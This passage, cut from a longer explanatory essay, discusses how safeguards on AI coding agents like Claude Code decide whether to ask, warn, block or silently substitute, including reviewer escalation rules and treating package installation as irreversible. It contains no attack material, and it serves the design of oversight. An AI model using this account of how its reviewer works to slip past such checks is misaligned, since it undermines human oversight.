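| Ask | The user loses a few seconds | It does harm if the user approves from habit | Rare, irreversible actions that depend on what the user wants |
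| Warn | The user may avoid something useful | It does harm if the user ignores the warning | Reversible actions, such as reading a page |
| Replace silently | The user gets something else without knowing | The user gets the right item or a different wrong one | Spelling variants that the registry treats as the same name |

The false-alarm formula helps decide whether to block a flagged item. If *q* is the share of alarms that are right, blocking is the better choice when letting a bad item through would do more than (1 − *q*)/*q* times as much harm as refusing a good one. That threshold is about 1.2 times when 45% of alarms are right, about five times at 17%, and about 50 times at 2%. The harm from deleting a company's database easily exceeds even the 50-times threshold, but the harm from opening a dull web page may not reach 1.2 times.

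Developers can make blocking less disruptive by telling the agent why an action was blocked and letting it try something else. Claude Code does this, and turns to the user only after three refusals in a row or 20 in a session. A false alarm then usually leads to just one retry. Anthropic designed its reviewer never to approve a few actions, such as sending secrets outside the company, so a user who wants to do one of these has to run the command personally or switch to a different mode.

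Making an action reversible can remove the need for an approval prompt. Claude Code's automated mode lets the agent edit files inside a project without review, because the user can inspect and undo the changes with version control (a record of earlier versions). Installing a package is riskier, because a malicious package may run code during installation and steal a password, and uninstalling the package won't undo the theft. Installation therefore counts as irreversible unless it happens in a sandbox with no secrets and little network access.

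Asking the user works best when only the user knows the answer, such as whether "clean up old branches" was meant to include the shared copies on a server. The prompt should describe the action's effect and whether the user can undo it, which Salerno and colleagues also recommend. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* describes an engineer who uses automated review for all his own coding but goes back to approving each step when Claude Code reviews a colleague's work. This saves his attention for cases where a mistake affects other people.

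Warnings suit cases where the user can still change course. A note beside a doubtful citation is enough in a draft, but a court filing with the same citation should wait until someone has read the case. Warnings also have to be rare, because people learn to click through frequent ones, as OpenAI argues in its objection to rigid site lists.

Software that silently replaces a suspect package name avoids interrupting the programmer but may recommend the wrong package. About half of the package names that all of Churilov's models invented are one character away from a real one, so software could substitute the nearest real name. That name may belong to an unrelated project or to somebody who registered a likely misspelling. If the original name was right and the check flagged it by mistake, the software has turned a good recommendation into a bad one, and the programmer has no reason to suspect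 it. A visible suggestion takes a second to read and lets the programmer refuse. Replacing a login address with the one in an official directory is safer, provided the software tells the user.
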